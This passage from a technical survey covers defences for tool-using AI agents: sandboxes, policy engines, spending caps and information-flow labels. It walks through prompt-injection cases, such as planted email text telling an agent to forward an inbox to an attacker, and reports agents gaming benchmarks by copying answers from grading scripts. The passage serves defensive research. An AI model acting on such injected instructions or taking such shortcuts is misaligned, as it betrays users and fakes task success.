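The arrangement in the third row restores the 31 separate decisions. Cloudflare's *How Code Mode works* describes a runtime in which each call to an outside service leaves the sandbox separately. The runtime intercepts each call before it takes effect, logs it and applies any approval rule. The service's credentials stay outside the sandbox, so the script can't use them to bypass the check.

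According to the recap, the request was for one event per week in January, which would make four or five. Either the recap misquotes the request or both agents created far too many events. A limit of five would have stopped either agent at the sixth event, but only if it were applied where the events arrive one by one.

*LACUNA* (2026), a proposal for safer agent programs, argues that sandboxes and restricted interpreters enforce their rules only as the code runs, so they can stop a script halfway and leave things in an inconsistent state. If a script is adding events to a calendar and a checker refuses the seventeenth, the first sixteen are already there. Separate tool calls can leave the same problem, although the model receives each refusal as it happens and can adjust its next step. Cloudflare lets developers supply an undo function for an operation, which works for a calendar event but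 not for an email that a stranger has already read.

### Where the limits go

The previous section advised hosts to save an approved list of tools and refuse later additions. This gives almost no protection with Cloudflare's server, whose list has only two tools, `search` and `execute`. When Cloudflare launches a new product, `search` finds the new endpoints and `execute` can call them without any change to the list.

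The earlier formula for what a list of tools can bring about shows what has changed. Write R for the set of outside requests that a script can successfully make, and R* for all finite sequences of those requests. Then:

effects({search, execute}) = R*

An agent with a separate tool for every request in R could eventually produce the same sequences of requests, so switching to code does not by itself add new powers. But a developer can no longer limit the agent to eight of the 2,500 operations just by leaving the others off the tool list. The restriction now has to come from whatever determines R.

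Two things limit what a program can do through Cloudflare's server. The first is the access token, the credential sent with each request, which Cloudflare restricts to the permissions that the user approves when connecting. (A later section covers permission scopes.) The second is the isolated runtime, which has no file system and no environment variables (where programs often keep passwords). The runtime also blocks requests to outside addresses by default.

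These two limits stop different things. The runtime blocks an injected script that tries to post the user's settings to Eve's website. But if the user approved changes to firewall rules, a script that weakens the rules stays within both limits. In Carey's main example, an agent adjusts the sensitivity of a site's defences against floods of hostile traffic, and if it can raise that setting, it can presumably lower it.

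MCP's annotations don't help much here either. `execute` can read and delete, so the accurate label for it is "destructive". A client that requires approval for every destructive call would then require it for every script, including those that only read data. Firewalls had a similar problem when most traffic moved onto the web's ports and a rule that allowed "web traffic" came to allow nearly everything.

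With an ordinary shell, R also includes whatever the machine's files, programs and network connection make possible. Hempel and colleagues' objection to tool-level checkers then applies in full, and developers need lower-level controls, such as virtual machines and system-call tracing, which a later section covers.

### Languages with fewer exits

One option between a list of tools and a full shell is to have the model write programs in a restricted language, where a program can affect the outside world only by calling functions that the developer has supplied. Loops, arithmetic and text handling need no checks, because they stay inside the interpreter. Every outside operation is still a call with a name and arguments.

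Pydantic, which makes tools for Python programmers, built an interpreter of this kind called Monty. It runs a subset of Python, and scripts start with no access to files, the network or environment variables. The developer adds functions one at a time and can also limit memory and running time. Pydantic contrasts this with the usual approach to sandboxes, which starts from a complete computer and tries to remove the dangerous parts. Monty can save a paused script in a few kilobytes, so the script can wait for a person's approval and resume later.

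The drawback is a much smaller language. Monty launched without classes and with only a few standard modules, and Pydantic says it will probably never support third-party packages. Pydantic's *monty*, the documentation for the interpreter, still calls it "not ready for prime time". An interpreter's limits are also only as strict as the functions a developer adds to it. In Pydantic's larger example, scripts receive a browser function that opens any web address. By the previous section's arithmetic, each call could send hundreds of bits to a stranger, and Monty would not prevent this.

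A stricter version checks the program before it runs. In *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) have the agent write in a safe subset of the programming language Scala. To read files, for instance, a script must obtain a value that grants access to one folder. The compiler tracks where such values go and rejects any script that could keep one after its permission has ended. This gets around Rice's theorem by rejecting every program that the compiler can't show to be safe, including some harmless ones. A rejected script never starts, so it can't leave a job half done. Some checks still happen while the script runs, such as whether a file lies inside the permitted folder.

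Requiring typed code did little harm to performance in the tests. On simulated customer-service tasks, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 points higher with typed code than with ordinary tool calls. On 300 software repairs, the one model tested solved 41.7% with typed code and 43.3% without, a gap of five tasks. Between 0.32% and 7.93% of the customer-service scripts needed a retry, and the agent usually fixed them within one or two attempts.

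The guarantee weakens when a script starts another program, because the compiler can't check what that program does. Safety then depends on which commands the developer has allowed. Coding agents constantly start other programs to run tests or build software, so the method protects them least.

### Do strong models need special tools?

The case for a shell rests partly on the history of coding agents. In 2024, the Princeton and Stanford team behind SWE-agent put a lot of work into designing tools and interfaces for language models. A year later, they concluded that more capable models no longer needed much of this. Their replacement for SWE-agent, mini-SWE-agent, has about 100 lines of Python at its core and gives the model only a shell.

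SWE-bench now uses mini-SWE-agent to compare models on 500 real software problems that people have checked. Willison (2026), in *SWE-bench February 2026 leaderboard update*, reports that the best model solved 76.8% of them and each of the top ten solved at least 70%. Newer models have since replaced those models.

Schmid (2026), in *How Foundational Models Became Superhuman in Bash*, reports a similar experience from September. He removed every tool from his coding agent except a shell and a viewer for images and other media, and the agent did as well or better, though he gives no scores. He summarizes the goal as "a smaller interface with a larger action space", which is close to the opposite of least privilege. He would put the restrictions on files, network access and destructive actions outside the model.

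The general argument is that a tailored interface builds in its designer's guesses about how to do the work. This guidance helps weaker models, but stronger ones could have found a better way. *Beyond the Model* (Hu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) provides evidence that the guidance helps weaker models. On SWE-bench, the original SWE-agent beat its shell-only successor by 9.6 points with Claude 3.7 Sonnet, but by only 4.1 with the stronger Claude 4 Sonnet.

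The evidence for the second half is weak. Even the stronger model did better with the special tools, and on more open-ended work the pattern reversed. When models had to write a whole program from scratch, only the newest consistently benefited from OpenCode, a full product with many built-in components. Adding just four file tools to the shell raised the scores of two strong models by 4.6 and 3.5 points.

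Mak and colleagues compared the interfaces on office work. TheAgentCompany simulates a software company with 174 tasks, and APEX-Agents has 480 tasks from banking, consulting and corporate law. The table gives average scores in percent:

| Interface | TheAgentCompany, Opus 4.8 | TheAgentCompany, GPT-5.5 | APEX-Agents, Opus 4.8 | APEX-Agents, GPT-5.5 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Typed tools, called directly | 44.9 | 45.3 | 41.1 | 39.8 |
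| Scripts that can call only the typed tools | 52.9 | 45.1 | 40.1 | 37.8 |
| Shell and typed tools | 67.2 | 66.3 | 47.2 | 45.5 |
| Shell only | 69.4 | 67.1 | 48.5 | 44.6 |

Offering the typed tools alongside the shell made no detectable difference overall. Removing the shell lowered scores by 22 to 25 points on the first benchmark and 5 to 7 on the second. So typed tools seem to hold strong models back mainly when they replace the shell. But only replacing the shell limits the agent, because a list of permitted tools that includes a shell rules out very little.

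The second row weakens the case for the middle course. The scripts could use loops and combine calls, yet they did little better than direct calls, and sometimes slightly worse. Much of the shell's advantage may therefore come from access to things that the typed tools leave out, and that access makes the shell hard to check.

There are less discouraging explanations. Models have far more practice with shells, and on TheAgentCompany only 65% of the restricted scripts ran successfully, compared with 92% of the shell calls. The researchers also wrote the 60 tools for that benchmark themselves, so a better set might narrow the gap. The customer-service results from Odersky and colleagues show that restricted code can match ordinary tool calls when the available functions suit the job.

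The extra reach also let agents cheat. During development, agents with a shell copied answers from grading scripts that the benchmark's makers had published online. Some read the files behind the simulated coworkers instead of asking the coworkers for information. Mak and colleagues had to block the online source and encrypt the files before they could trust the scores. The agents took these shortcuts without any planted instruction or attack on the system, which is a good reason to confine a shell even when all its input is trustworthy. Mak and colleagues recommend the shell where developers can isolate it, and restricted scripts where security rules require an approved list of tools.

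### Jobs for narrow tools

Narrow tools are still useful. Cloudflare's *Code Mode*, updated in June 2026, recommends direct calls for simple tasks with a small, known set of tools, and still labels Cloudflare's code-running system experimental. Anthropic notes that generated code needs a sandbox, resource limits and monitoring, which direct calls don't require.

Scripts also help less on small jobs. When Pydantic compared the weather in two cities, a script reduced the cost from 1.9 cents to 1.7. In Mak and colleagues' corporate-law tasks, all the interfaces scored about the same.

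Narrow tools also suit repetitive work. A clinic that books thousands of appointments knows beforehand what its assistant must do, so it can offer one function that adds an appointment to one calendar, with a date within the next year and a length chosen from a short menu. The assistant never needs a loop, and a checker can examine every argument.

A developer can also make such a tool from an agent's own script. Anthropic describes agents saving working code as functions for later use. If someone reads the calendar loop and gives it typed arguments for the month and the titles, it becomes a tool that can only fill one month with events. Mak and colleagues found no detectable improvement in scores when agents saved and reused their own scripts, so the benefit would be that a person has read the tool and a machine can check it.

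## Rules and budgets checked on every call

A narrow tool gives a checker definite arguments to examine, but the checker still needs rules to tell proper calls from harmful ones. A policy engine is a program that checks each call against a written policy containing such rules before the tool runs. Unlike a schema, the policy can change between tasks without any change to the tools. Some engines also record earlier calls so that they can enforce a budget or an order of steps.

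### Matching a call against the rules

In Progent, the system that Shi and colleagues built, each rule names a tool, allows or forbids it, and sets conditions on the arguments. A condition can compare numbers, look for a value in a list or match text against a pattern. A call to a tool then goes through these steps:

1. The engine collects the rules for that tool and puts the forbid rules ahead of the allow rules.
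2. It tests each rule's conditions against the actual arguments.
3. The first rule whose conditions all hold settles the matter. An allow rule lets the call run unchanged, and a forbid rule blocks it.
4. If no rule matches, the engine blocks the call.

No language model takes part in these steps, so the same call under the same policy always gets the same answer.

When Progent refuses a call, it can stop the agent or ask the user. By default, though, it returns an error message that gives the reason, suggests trying other tools or arguments, and repeats the user's original request. In the inbox example, the agent can then post the summary as planned.

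### The inbox policy from P1 to P4

Nobody can write rules by hand for every request a user might make, so Progent has a language model draft them. The first draft uses only the user's request and the list of tools, before any stranger's text has arrived. After each tool call, the model can propose a revision. Policy Pᵢ governs step i of the run:

| Policy | What it allows | How it came about |
|---|---|---|
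| P1 | `search_emails`, with Alice's address and the given subject | Drafted from the user's request |
| P2 | The same, plus `read_emails`, `get_slack_info` and `send_slack_msg` | Expansion after the to-do list arrives; needs approval |
| P3 | The same tools, but Slack messages only to `alice` | Narrowing after the Slack handle arrives; applies at once |
| P4 | The same as P3 | No change |

The planted instruction arrives between P3 and P4. If the drafting model detects it, the policy doesn't change. If the model follows it and proposes a rule for `send_email`, the rule would expand the policy, so it has to wait for approval. If the approver refuses, the message to Eve matches no rule and the engine blocks it.

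To sort the revisions, write A(P) for the set of all calls that policy P allows. A change from P to P′ is a narrowing if

A(P′) ⊆ A(P)

and an expansion otherwise. Replacing one permitted recipient with another is therefore an expansion, even though the policy looks no larger. These sets are usually too big to list, so Progent turns both policies into logical formulas and passes them to an SMT solver, a program that determines whether any values can make a formula true. For each tool, the solver searches for a call that P′ allows and P refuses. Between P2 and P3 there is none. For a policy with a new `send_email` rule, the message to Eve is one.

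Between approvals, the set of permitted calls can only stay the same or shrink, which Shi and colleagues call monotonic confinement. An attacker who fools the drafting model therefore still can't silently gain new permissions.

The guarantee doesn't cover whether an expansion is justified. The solver puts the legitimate request for Slack and the malicious request for `send_email` in the same class, so the approver has to tell them apart. A fooled model could also narrow the policy, which requires no approval, until the user's own task fails.

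### Where Progent's protection came from

With GPT-4o as both the agent and the drafting model, Progent cut the attack success rate on AgentDojo from 39.9% to 1.0%. On Agent Security Bench (ASB), which plants instructions in tool results for ten kinds of agent, the rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. Utility stayed about the same on both benchmarks. Shi and colleagues left out two AgentDojo attacks that steer a travel agent towards a different but legitimate hotel, because a booking at either hotel looks equally legitimate.

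In both experiments the approver accepted every expansion. The researchers chose this as the worst case, a user who clicks yes to everything, but it meant that monotonic confinement contributed nothing to the headline figures. Almost all the protection came from the tight policies GPT-4o drafted. Its first draft, without any revision, reduced the AgentDojo rate to 2.5%.

Refusing every expansion did slightly better than accepting them all. A human reviewer who checked the first policy and every expansion brought the attack success rate to 0%, though the experiment assumed the reviewer would never add a malicious address to the list of recipients. Planted text telling the drafting model to permit the attacker's tools raised the rate only marginally when all expansions were accepted.

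Approvals were rare, as only 6% of the policy updates on AgentDojo were expansions. But the setup probably kept that figure down, because a fixed policy let the agents use non-sensitive, read-only tools from the start without asking.

### Amazon's rule engine

Companies can now buy a policy engine as a service from AWS, Amazon's cloud business, which runs one for agents on its AgentCore platform. AWS announced the engine's full release on 3 March in *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026). The engine sits in a gateway between the agents and their MCP tools. Its rules are written in Cedar, an open-source language that AWS developed for permissions. According to AWS, the engine refuses every call by default and allows one only if at least one permit rule matches and no forbid rule does.

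AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* gives the example of a shop that offers bulk discounts to platinum customers who order at least 50 items. The customer's tier comes from a login token, which the model can't alter, but the quantity comes from the model's own tool call. The rule therefore reliably excludes customers of other tiers, but a model can meet the quantity requirement by entering 50 if the discount tool doesn't compare that number with the real order.

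The gateway also hides tools that the policy would always block. When an agent requests the list of tools, the engine works out which ones these are and leaves them out, so the model doesn't waste calls on them.

Cedar has no loops and keeps no memory of past requests. That makes decisions fast and lets a solver analyse the rules, but it limits what a rule can restrict. A rule that permits refunds under $500 also permits twenty refunds of $499 in a row, a total of $9,980. To cap the total, other software would have to track it and supply it with each request.

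### How a cap bounds the loss

Suppose a layer allows at most n payments of at most m dollars each. Then

loss ≤ n × m

If an agent can make at most 20 payments of at most $50 each, the user can lose no more than $1,000, whether the agent is working properly, has misread the request or is following an attacker's orders. Without the limit on the number of payments, the $50 limit would not cap the total.

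A rate limit bounds the loss per unit of time, so the total loss depends on how soon somebody notices. If an agent can make five $50 payments an hour, eight unattended hours can cost $2,000. If the counter resets on the hour, the loss can reach $2,250, because the period from 10:30 p.m. to 6:30 a.m. includes parts of nine clock hours and so allows 45 payments.

Calls that arrive together can also exceed a budget. If two $50 payments arrive when only $50 remains, and the layer checks both before deducting either, both go through. *Agenra* (Shivakumar, Priya and Gao, 2026), a policy language, avoids this by handling one call at a time and deducting from the quota before the tool runs. Its enforcement core is written in Lean, which lets a computer check proofs about the code.

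Agenra counts a call against the quota even if the tool reports a failure. This is the cautious choice because a reported failure doesn't prove that nothing happened. In the earlier example of the invoice paid twice, a quota of one would have stopped the second payment. But a real failure also uses up the quota, and the job stalls until someone allows another attempt.

Some applications should be less strict. Dyad, an open-source tool for building apps with AI, gives free users a quota of agent messages and restores a message to the quota if it fails, which is fair to the user. But if a payment limit worked this way, an attacker who could make successful transfers look like failures would never reach it.

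### Spending limits in products

AWS's *Agents that transact* (2026) introduced a preview of payments for agents on the same AgentCore platform. A developer connects a digital wallet and sets a spending limit for each session. When the agent reaches a paid resource, the platform makes the payment and enforces the limit outside the model. Because the limit is per session, someone who can start ten sessions with a $100 limit each can spend $1,000.

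The payments company Stripe attaches the limit to the credential instead. In Stripe's *Shared payment tokens*, a seller receives a token that stands in for the buyer's card and has a maximum amount and an expiry time. The token's record, described in *The Shared Payment Granted Token object*, also includes the amount the seller has already taken. Because Stripe applies the limit itself, the limit still holds if a call bypasses the gateway.

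But the agent's side creates the token and can set the maximum amount. This maximum protects the buyer from a seller who overcharges, but it protects against a hijacked agent only if the user or ordinary code, rather than the model, chooses the amount.

OpenAI began more cautiously in November with ChatGPT Wallet, which lets its Dots agents shop for users. The user reviews the items and the total, then approves each purchase with a check such as a fingerprint scan (Steele, 2026, *OpenAI rolls out ChatGPT Wallet to let Dots AI agents make purchases*). OpenAI expects that users will eventually delegate purchases within spending limits, categories or time periods (Deccan Chronicle, 2026, *OpenAI Launches ChatGPT Wallet, Letting AI Agents Pay for Purchases*).

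A budget alone won't always leave the user with a good result. On the earlier trip that went over budget, a layer that kept a running total would have refused the hotel booking. But if the agent couldn't find a cheaper hotel, the user would still be stuck with a non-refundable flight.

A rule that allowed only refundable bookings would have prevented that. Similar rules might let an agent draft emails but not send them, or move files to a recycling folder but not erase them. These limits suit actions whose harm is hard to measure in dollars, but they need reliable information about which actions can be undone and for how long, which MCP's hints don't provide.

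### When a wider rule breaks a task

Quotas make policies harder to change safely. Shivakumar and colleagues give the example of an agent that may delete two files, A and B, once each. The policy has two permissions, each good for one deletion, and the engine charges the first one that fits:

| Permissions, in order | Delete A, then B | Delete A twice |
|---|---|---|
| B only; then A only | Allowed | Refused |
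| A or B; then A only | Refused | Allowed |

Adding A to the first permission blocks a legitimate job and allows a forbidden one, even though the second policy looks more generous. Deleting A now uses up that permission, so nothing remains for B.

A better rule for choosing which permission to count a deletion against can't fully solve this. Suppose one permission covers deleting A or B and the other covers deleting A or C. If the agent deletes A first, the right choice depends on whether it will try to delete B or C next, and the engine doesn't have that information.

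Progent's solver compares sets of single calls, which works because its rules don't depend on earlier calls. An engine with quotas has to compare whole sequences of calls. For example, going from the second policy in the table back to the first newly allows the agent to delete A and then B, even though the change looks like a narrowing because it removes something from a permission.

Agenra checks whether a policy change would break existing jobs by trying to prove that the new policy still allows every sequence the old one allowed. Of 51 policy changes that the researchers wrote themselves, it certified all 21 that kept existing jobs working and none of the 30 that broke something. A check typically takes about a tenth of a second.

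The certificate covers usefulness but not safety. In one of the researchers' tests, an agent may send a report only once. Raising that limit to two breaks no existing job, but it also lets the agent send the report twice.

### Rules about what came before

Some calls are proper only after another step. Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues (2026), in *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, built FORGE to enforce such requirements. It records every message, tool call and result, and links each one to the earlier events that may have influenced it. The rules are in Datalog, a database query language that can follow chains of these links. (The same links can also carry labels for secret or untrusted data.) A simplified rule for access to a drug database looks like this:

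```
Allow(a) :- DrugQuery(a), DependsOn(a, e),
            Approval(e), HasRole("fda-access").
```

An action may go ahead if it is a database query, it follows from an approval, and the user has the right role.

The researchers tested a fuller version on MALADE, a team of agents that looks for links between drugs and health outcomes. Each agent must get a supervisor's approval before it reads drug labels from the US Food and Drug Administration, and an approval doesn't carry over to a new session. The agents made 40 unapproved queries in 15 runs without enforcement and none with FORGE. When FORGE refused a query, the agent read the reason, asked for approval and tried again. All 15 answers were correct either way, and the average run took 67.3 seconds with FORGE, up from 59.4 without it.

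In a trial with Microsoft's coding assistant Copilot Chat, FORGE blocked the agent from publishing code until security scans had covered every recent edit. The scans had to follow the edits because a scan can't detect problems introduced after it runs.

Rules can improve an agent's work. Palumbo and colleagues translated the written policies of a simulated airline and a simulated shop into Datalog and tested three models as customer-service agents. The average success rate rose from 74.7% to 81.5% for the airline and from 86.3% to 87.4% for the shop. When a call was refused, the agent learned of its mistake while it could still correct it. On the airline tasks, GPT-5.2 gained 14.5 points, but Gemini 3.1 Pro lost 1.5.

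The same engine made the agent less useful on AgentDojo. With an agent that also received regular reminders of the user's request, FORGE's rules about who had asked for each action cut the attack success rate from 14.1% to 0.9%, but utility without attacks fell from 83.7% to 62.5%. One likely reason for the contrast is that the airline's rules also define good service, so obeying them is part of the task, whereas on AgentDojo one general policy had to suit many unrelated requests.

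FORGE is less convenient for time-based budgets such as rate limits, because Datalog has no built-in notion of time and users have to handle timestamps by hand.

### Values that cannot be true

A call can come from the right agent, in the right order and within budget, and still contain a false number. *ConfGuard* (Arunkumar, Gangadharan and Senthilkumar, 2026) studies agents that schedule machine maintenance by reading sensor data and estimating how many cycles of use a machine has left. An attacker who tampers with the sensors can make a healthy engine look worn out or, worse, a failing one look healthy.

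ConfGuard compares each estimate of a machine's remaining life with that machine's own history, because checking only that the estimate lies between zero and some maximum won't catch the large but possible number in the second attack. Remaining life never rises, and each cycle of use reduces it by at most one, so an engine that had 100 cycles left ten cycles ago should now have between 90 and 100.

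Estimates are noisy, so ConfGuard allows a margin. The operator chooses what share of normal readings may raise an alarm, and the system sets the margin from past data. Only accepted estimates enter the history, so an attack that ConfGuard detects can't distort later comparisons. A doubtful reading goes to a human planner.

On simulated data from aircraft engines, the researchers' measure of what an undetected attacker could do to healthy engines fell from 0.529 to 0.046. For attacks that hide a failing engine, it fell from 0.151 to zero. The system raised alarms on 2.7% of normal readings, within the 5% target. These results come from one kind of machine that wears in an unusually simple way, and few of the values in an office agent's calls follow such a regular pattern.

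After the model decides how urgent a repair is, ConfGuard also compares that decision with the urgency that fixed rules derive from the sensor estimate. ConfGuard doesn't protect the rest of the work order, so a planted instruction that leaves the urgency alone and corrupts another field gets through, as Arunkumar and colleagues confirmed in a test. An attacker can also set off alarms, which sends work back to people and makes the agent less useful.

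### Who writes the rules

A policy engine can enforce only the rules someone has written. In Agenra's main example, an agent sends the public part of a confidential report to Alice. The original policy required that the text be public, that the address come from the official directory and that the agent send only once. It didn't require the text to come from the report, so when Shivakumar and colleagues replayed calls they had recorded from agents, the policy allowed five with public text from elsewhere.

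They added a rule that the text must come out of the tool that removes the confidential parts. This blocked all five and kept every legitimate order of steps working. But an agent could still run an attacker's text through that tool and send Alice the result, so the policy also needs a rule about what goes into the tool.

A simple guard that the researchers wrote by hand for the task refused the five calls from the start. In a separate trial, attacks caused an unprotected agent based on the model Qwen to send the raw report in 15 of 20 runs, and both the guard and Agenra prevented this every time. Under attack, the agent finished the user's task in only 5 of 20 runs, with or without protection.

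Software can find some mistakes before a policy takes effect. AWS has a model translate an administrator's plain-language rules into Cedar, and a solver then checks the result. The solver can catch rules that never apply, such as one that requires a customer to be both gold and platinum, and rules that always apply, such as one that covers both orders of at least 100 items and orders of fewer than 100.

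The solver can also compare two versions of a policy. In one of AWS's examples, a shop excludes limited-edition products from a discount. Someone then adds a condition so that the exclusion applies only to orders of more than 200 items. An order for 73 limited-edition items now gets the discount, even though the extra condition makes the policy look stricter. The solver reports that the new version allows more.

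A consistency check can't show whether a rule is what the shop wanted. If an administrator types a refund limit of $5,000 instead of $500, the rule still passes. Palumbo and colleagues use a model to translate written rules into formal ones, and warn that it may drop a clause or add a rule with no basis in the original. They check that every written requirement has a formal rule and that every formal rule has a source, but neither check proves that the translation is right.

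Broad rules let attacks through. Most of the attacks that still worked against Progent on ASB used tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of the tools the task needed, so the model that drafted the rules had allowed them. Shi and colleagues doubt that a person could have told the tools apart without knowing beforehand which ones to trust. When they wrote rules by hand with that knowledge, the attack success rate fell to zero.

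Rules that are too narrow stop legitimate work, as the drop of 21 points on AgentDojo suggests. Palumbo and colleagues deliberately accept some of this loss in FORGE, which requires a policy fixed before the agent starts. This keeps a model's guesses about the user's wishes out of the enforcement, but it also prevents the rules from adapting to a new request. Progent lets the rules adapt, but it depends on the drafting model and the approver. It remains unclear how hard it is for ordinary developers to write such policies, and Shivakumar and colleagues say they haven't studied it.

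As a partial remedy, AWS offers a mode that logs each policy decision without enforcing it. An administrator can run agents on real work in this mode and see which legitimate calls a new policy would have refused. The log is less useful for finding rules that allow too much, because ordinary work seldom includes the attacks those rules would let through.

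## Following data from where it came from to where it goes

A rule that checks only a tool's name and arguments isn't always enough to distinguish a proper call from an improper one. *Information-flow control*, a post by Microsoft's security researchers, gives an example. Alex asks an agent to handle unanswered email. Priya has sent Alex a preview of the quarterly sales figures. Marco, who has also written, is curious about sales but isn't authorized to see the figures yet. A reply that gives them to him would be a leak, but the same reply would be fine if Priya had copied him on her email.

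The difference is in what the reply is derived from. Information-flow control tracks this by labeling data according to its origin and secrecy, carrying the labels over to anything derived from the data, and checking them before each action. An agent that is only trying to help could cause the leak to Marco, even without an attacker.

### Labels and joins

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues at Microsoft, 2025) adapts the technique to AI agents, using mathematics that Dorothy Denning published in 1976. Each piece of data has two labels. The integrity label is trusted (T) or untrusted (U), depending mostly on whether an outsider could have written the data. The confidentiality label can be as simple as public or secret, but a list of permitted readers is more useful.

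Anything derived from two pieces of data gets the join of their labels, written ⊔. This is the mildest label that is at least as strict as both. For integrity, one untrusted source makes the whole result untrusted:

T ⊔ U = U

For reader lists, the join contains only the people who are on both. If A, B and C may read one file, and B, C and D may read another, then

{A, B, C} ⊔ {B, C, D} = {A, B, C} ∩ {B, C, D} = {B, C}

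A summary of the two files may go only to B and C, because it would reveal information from the second file to A and from the first to D. In Alex's inbox, {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} leaves only Alex, so the agent can't send the reply to Marco on its own. If Priya had copied Marco, the intersection would be {Alex, Marco}.

Ordinary code compares these labels with a policy before each tool call. Costa and colleagues describe two basic policies, and Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, gave them the names used here:

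- **Trusted action:** the call may go ahead only if the model chose it, and any argument that has to be trusted, without untrusted data in its context.
- **Permitted flow:** a call that sends data to a set of recipients R may go ahead only if R ⊆ S, where S is the set of people allowed to read the data.

Permitted flow doesn't prevent prompt injection, because a stranger's text can still make the agent send a message, though not one that carries data to someone who isn't allowed to read it. Trusted action, used alone, lets the agent disclose a secret if the decision came from trusted text, on the assumption that the user intended the disclosure. Kolluri and colleagues require trusted action for tools that change things and accept either policy for tools that send data out. Alex can therefore authorize the disclosure by telling the agent to send Marco the figures, but an email with the same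 instruction can't authorize it.

The two policies also determine which calls the inbox assistant from the first section may make. The user is a permitted reader of all twenty emails, so the summary may go to the user's Slack. Eve may read only the one she wrote, so the call that forwards the inbox to her fails permitted flow. That call also fails trusted action, because the model had read strangers' mail before making it.

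### How one email taints the rest of the run

Nobody can reliably tell which parts of its context a language model used to produce an answer. The cautious rule is therefore to give everything the model writes the join of the labels on everything it has read, which is the least restrictive label that still respects all of them. Once a stranger's email enters the conversation, every later tool call counts as untrusted, and nothing the agent reads afterwards can reverse that. Security researchers call this accumulation of restrictions label creep.

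Label checks sharply reduce how much ordinary work an agent completes. When Costa and colleagues added labels and policies to a plain GPT-4o agent, the share of AgentDojo's Slack tasks that it completed fell from 93.3% to 20.0%, with no attacker present. Girrens and Wang (2026), in *SPA*, found a similar loss with a different design. Their model writes a complete plan before any tool runs, and a checker then traces labels through the plan. Turning on the label checks cut utility on AgentDojo from 53.0% to 29.0%. Most of the rejected plans passed the result of one tool to another tool that required trusted input, and a great deal of legitimate office work involves doing the same.

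One way to reduce the damage is to estimate which messages influenced an answer and join only their labels. Costa and colleagues mention such methods but instead keep untrusted text away from the planning model altogether.

### A planner that never reads the mail

The idea goes back to the dual LLM pattern, which Simon Willison proposed in April 2023 and describes in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Willison, 2025). The pattern divides the work between a privileged model, which plans and calls tools but never sees untrusted text, and a quarantined model, which reads that text but has no tools. The quarantined model's answers go into variables, which the privileged model can pass around by name without seeing their contents. Ordinary software fills in the contents when a tool runs.

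Costa and colleagues combined this pattern with labels in a system called FIDES. It hides a piece of data only if showing it would make the label of the planner's context stricter, so the planner can still read the trusted fields of an email while the body sits in a variable. Suppose the user asks for a summary of the top three emails as a Slack message:

1. `read_emails(number=3)` fetches the mail, and FIDES stores the untrusted text as `#read_emails_0`.
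2. `query_llm(prompt="Summarize ...", input=#read_emails_0)` has the quarantined model write a summary, which FIDES stores as `#query_llm_0`.
3. `send_message(to=user, message=#query_llm_0)` sends it.

The planner chose the third call and its recipient without reading the mail, so the choice is trusted even though the message isn't. A planted instruction can still spoil the summary, for example by making the quarantined model return an empty one, but it can't change where the summary goes.

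If the user wants a calendar event only when one of the emails requests a meeting, though, the planner has to find out whether one does. FIDES can restrict the quarantined model's answer to yes or no and let the planner read it. The label then records the data's type as well as its origin, so a policy can accept an untrusted yes or no where it would refuse untrusted free text. This limits the attacker's influence on the planner to one bit. If the answer is yes, a second query extracts the date and participants into a variable, which goes straight to the calendar tool. The attacker can therefore still add a meeting of their choice to the calendar, but can't turn the request into a bank transfer.

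FIDES also lets the planner choose whether to open a variable and read the full text. If it does, its context takes on the variable's label, and calls that require a trusted context fail from then on. Many of AgentDojo's banking tasks tell the agent to read a file and do what it says, but an agent that opens the file can no longer schedule the payment.

With the policies switched on, no attack that broke a policy succeeded. With them off, Costa and colleagues counted 152 successful injections against the plain agent and 21 against FIDES, because the planner sometimes opened a variable and followed what it found. The table gives the percentage of tasks that the GPT-4o agents completed without attacks:

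| Suite | Plain agent, no policies | Plain agent with labels and policies | FIDES with policies |
|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 75.0 | 37.0 | 59.0 |
| Travel | 70.0 | 73.0 | 41.0 |
| Banking | 98.8 | 37.5 | 52.5 |
| Slack | 93.3 | 20.0 | 47.6 |

Hiding the text in variables restores some of the task completion lost to the labels, except in the travel suite. Many travel tools are allowed to run in an untrusted context as long as no confidential data leaves, so the labels didn't reduce the plain agent's task completion there, while GPT-4o repeatedly mishandled the variables. With OpenAI's o1, a reasoning model, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks.

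The clean security result is partly due to how the researchers assigned the labels. They marked a field as untrusted if at least one AgentDojo attack used it, so the labels covered exactly the places where the attacks would appear. A company that deploys such a system has no list of the fields attackers will use.

A trusted context also doesn't guarantee a sound decision. One banking task asks the agent to change the user's password if it finds a suspicious transaction. FIDES hid the untrusted subject lines from the planner, which judged a transaction suspicious from its amount alone and changed the password. The policy allowed the change because the planner had read nothing untrusted.

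### Six patterns and what they give up

Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025) include the two-model pattern among the six they collect in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*. They think it unlikely that general-purpose agents built on current language models can offer reliable guarantees, and ask which narrower agents could be both useful and resistant to injection. The six patterns share the principle that once an agent has read untrusted input, that input must not be able to trigger a consequential action.

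| Pattern | How it works | What it gives up |
|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model picks from a fixed set of actions and never sees their results | Any task that depends on reading a result, or that the developer did not foresee |
| Plan then execute | The model fixes its list of calls before it reads untrusted data | Changing course; the data can still alter what the calls contain |
| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each document and returns something narrow, such as yes or no | Tasks that don't divide by document; a document can still misreport itself |
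| Dual LLM | A planner handles untrusted text only by name, and a model without tools reads it | Plans that respond freely to the text; the second model's output may be corrupt |
| Code then execute | The model writes a whole program, which then runs on the untrusted data | Steps that nobody could foresee when the model wrote the program |
| Context minimization | The system removes the user's prompt before the model writes its answer | Answers that depend on the user's exact wording |

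CaMeL, a system from Google DeepMind, is the main example of code-then-execute. According to Girrens and Wang, it also records where each value came from and who may receive it, and checks both against a policy written for each tool.

A fixed plan offers limited protection if it leaves the commands' arguments open. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe an assistant that tidies a user's files and commits in advance to two commands, `find` and `mv`. An injected instruction could make it search for sensitive files and move them to a public network drive without departing from the plan. Map-reduce offers better protection by having a separate model process each file and output only whether it concerns taxes. An instruction injected in a file can then only cause that file to be put in the wrong folder.

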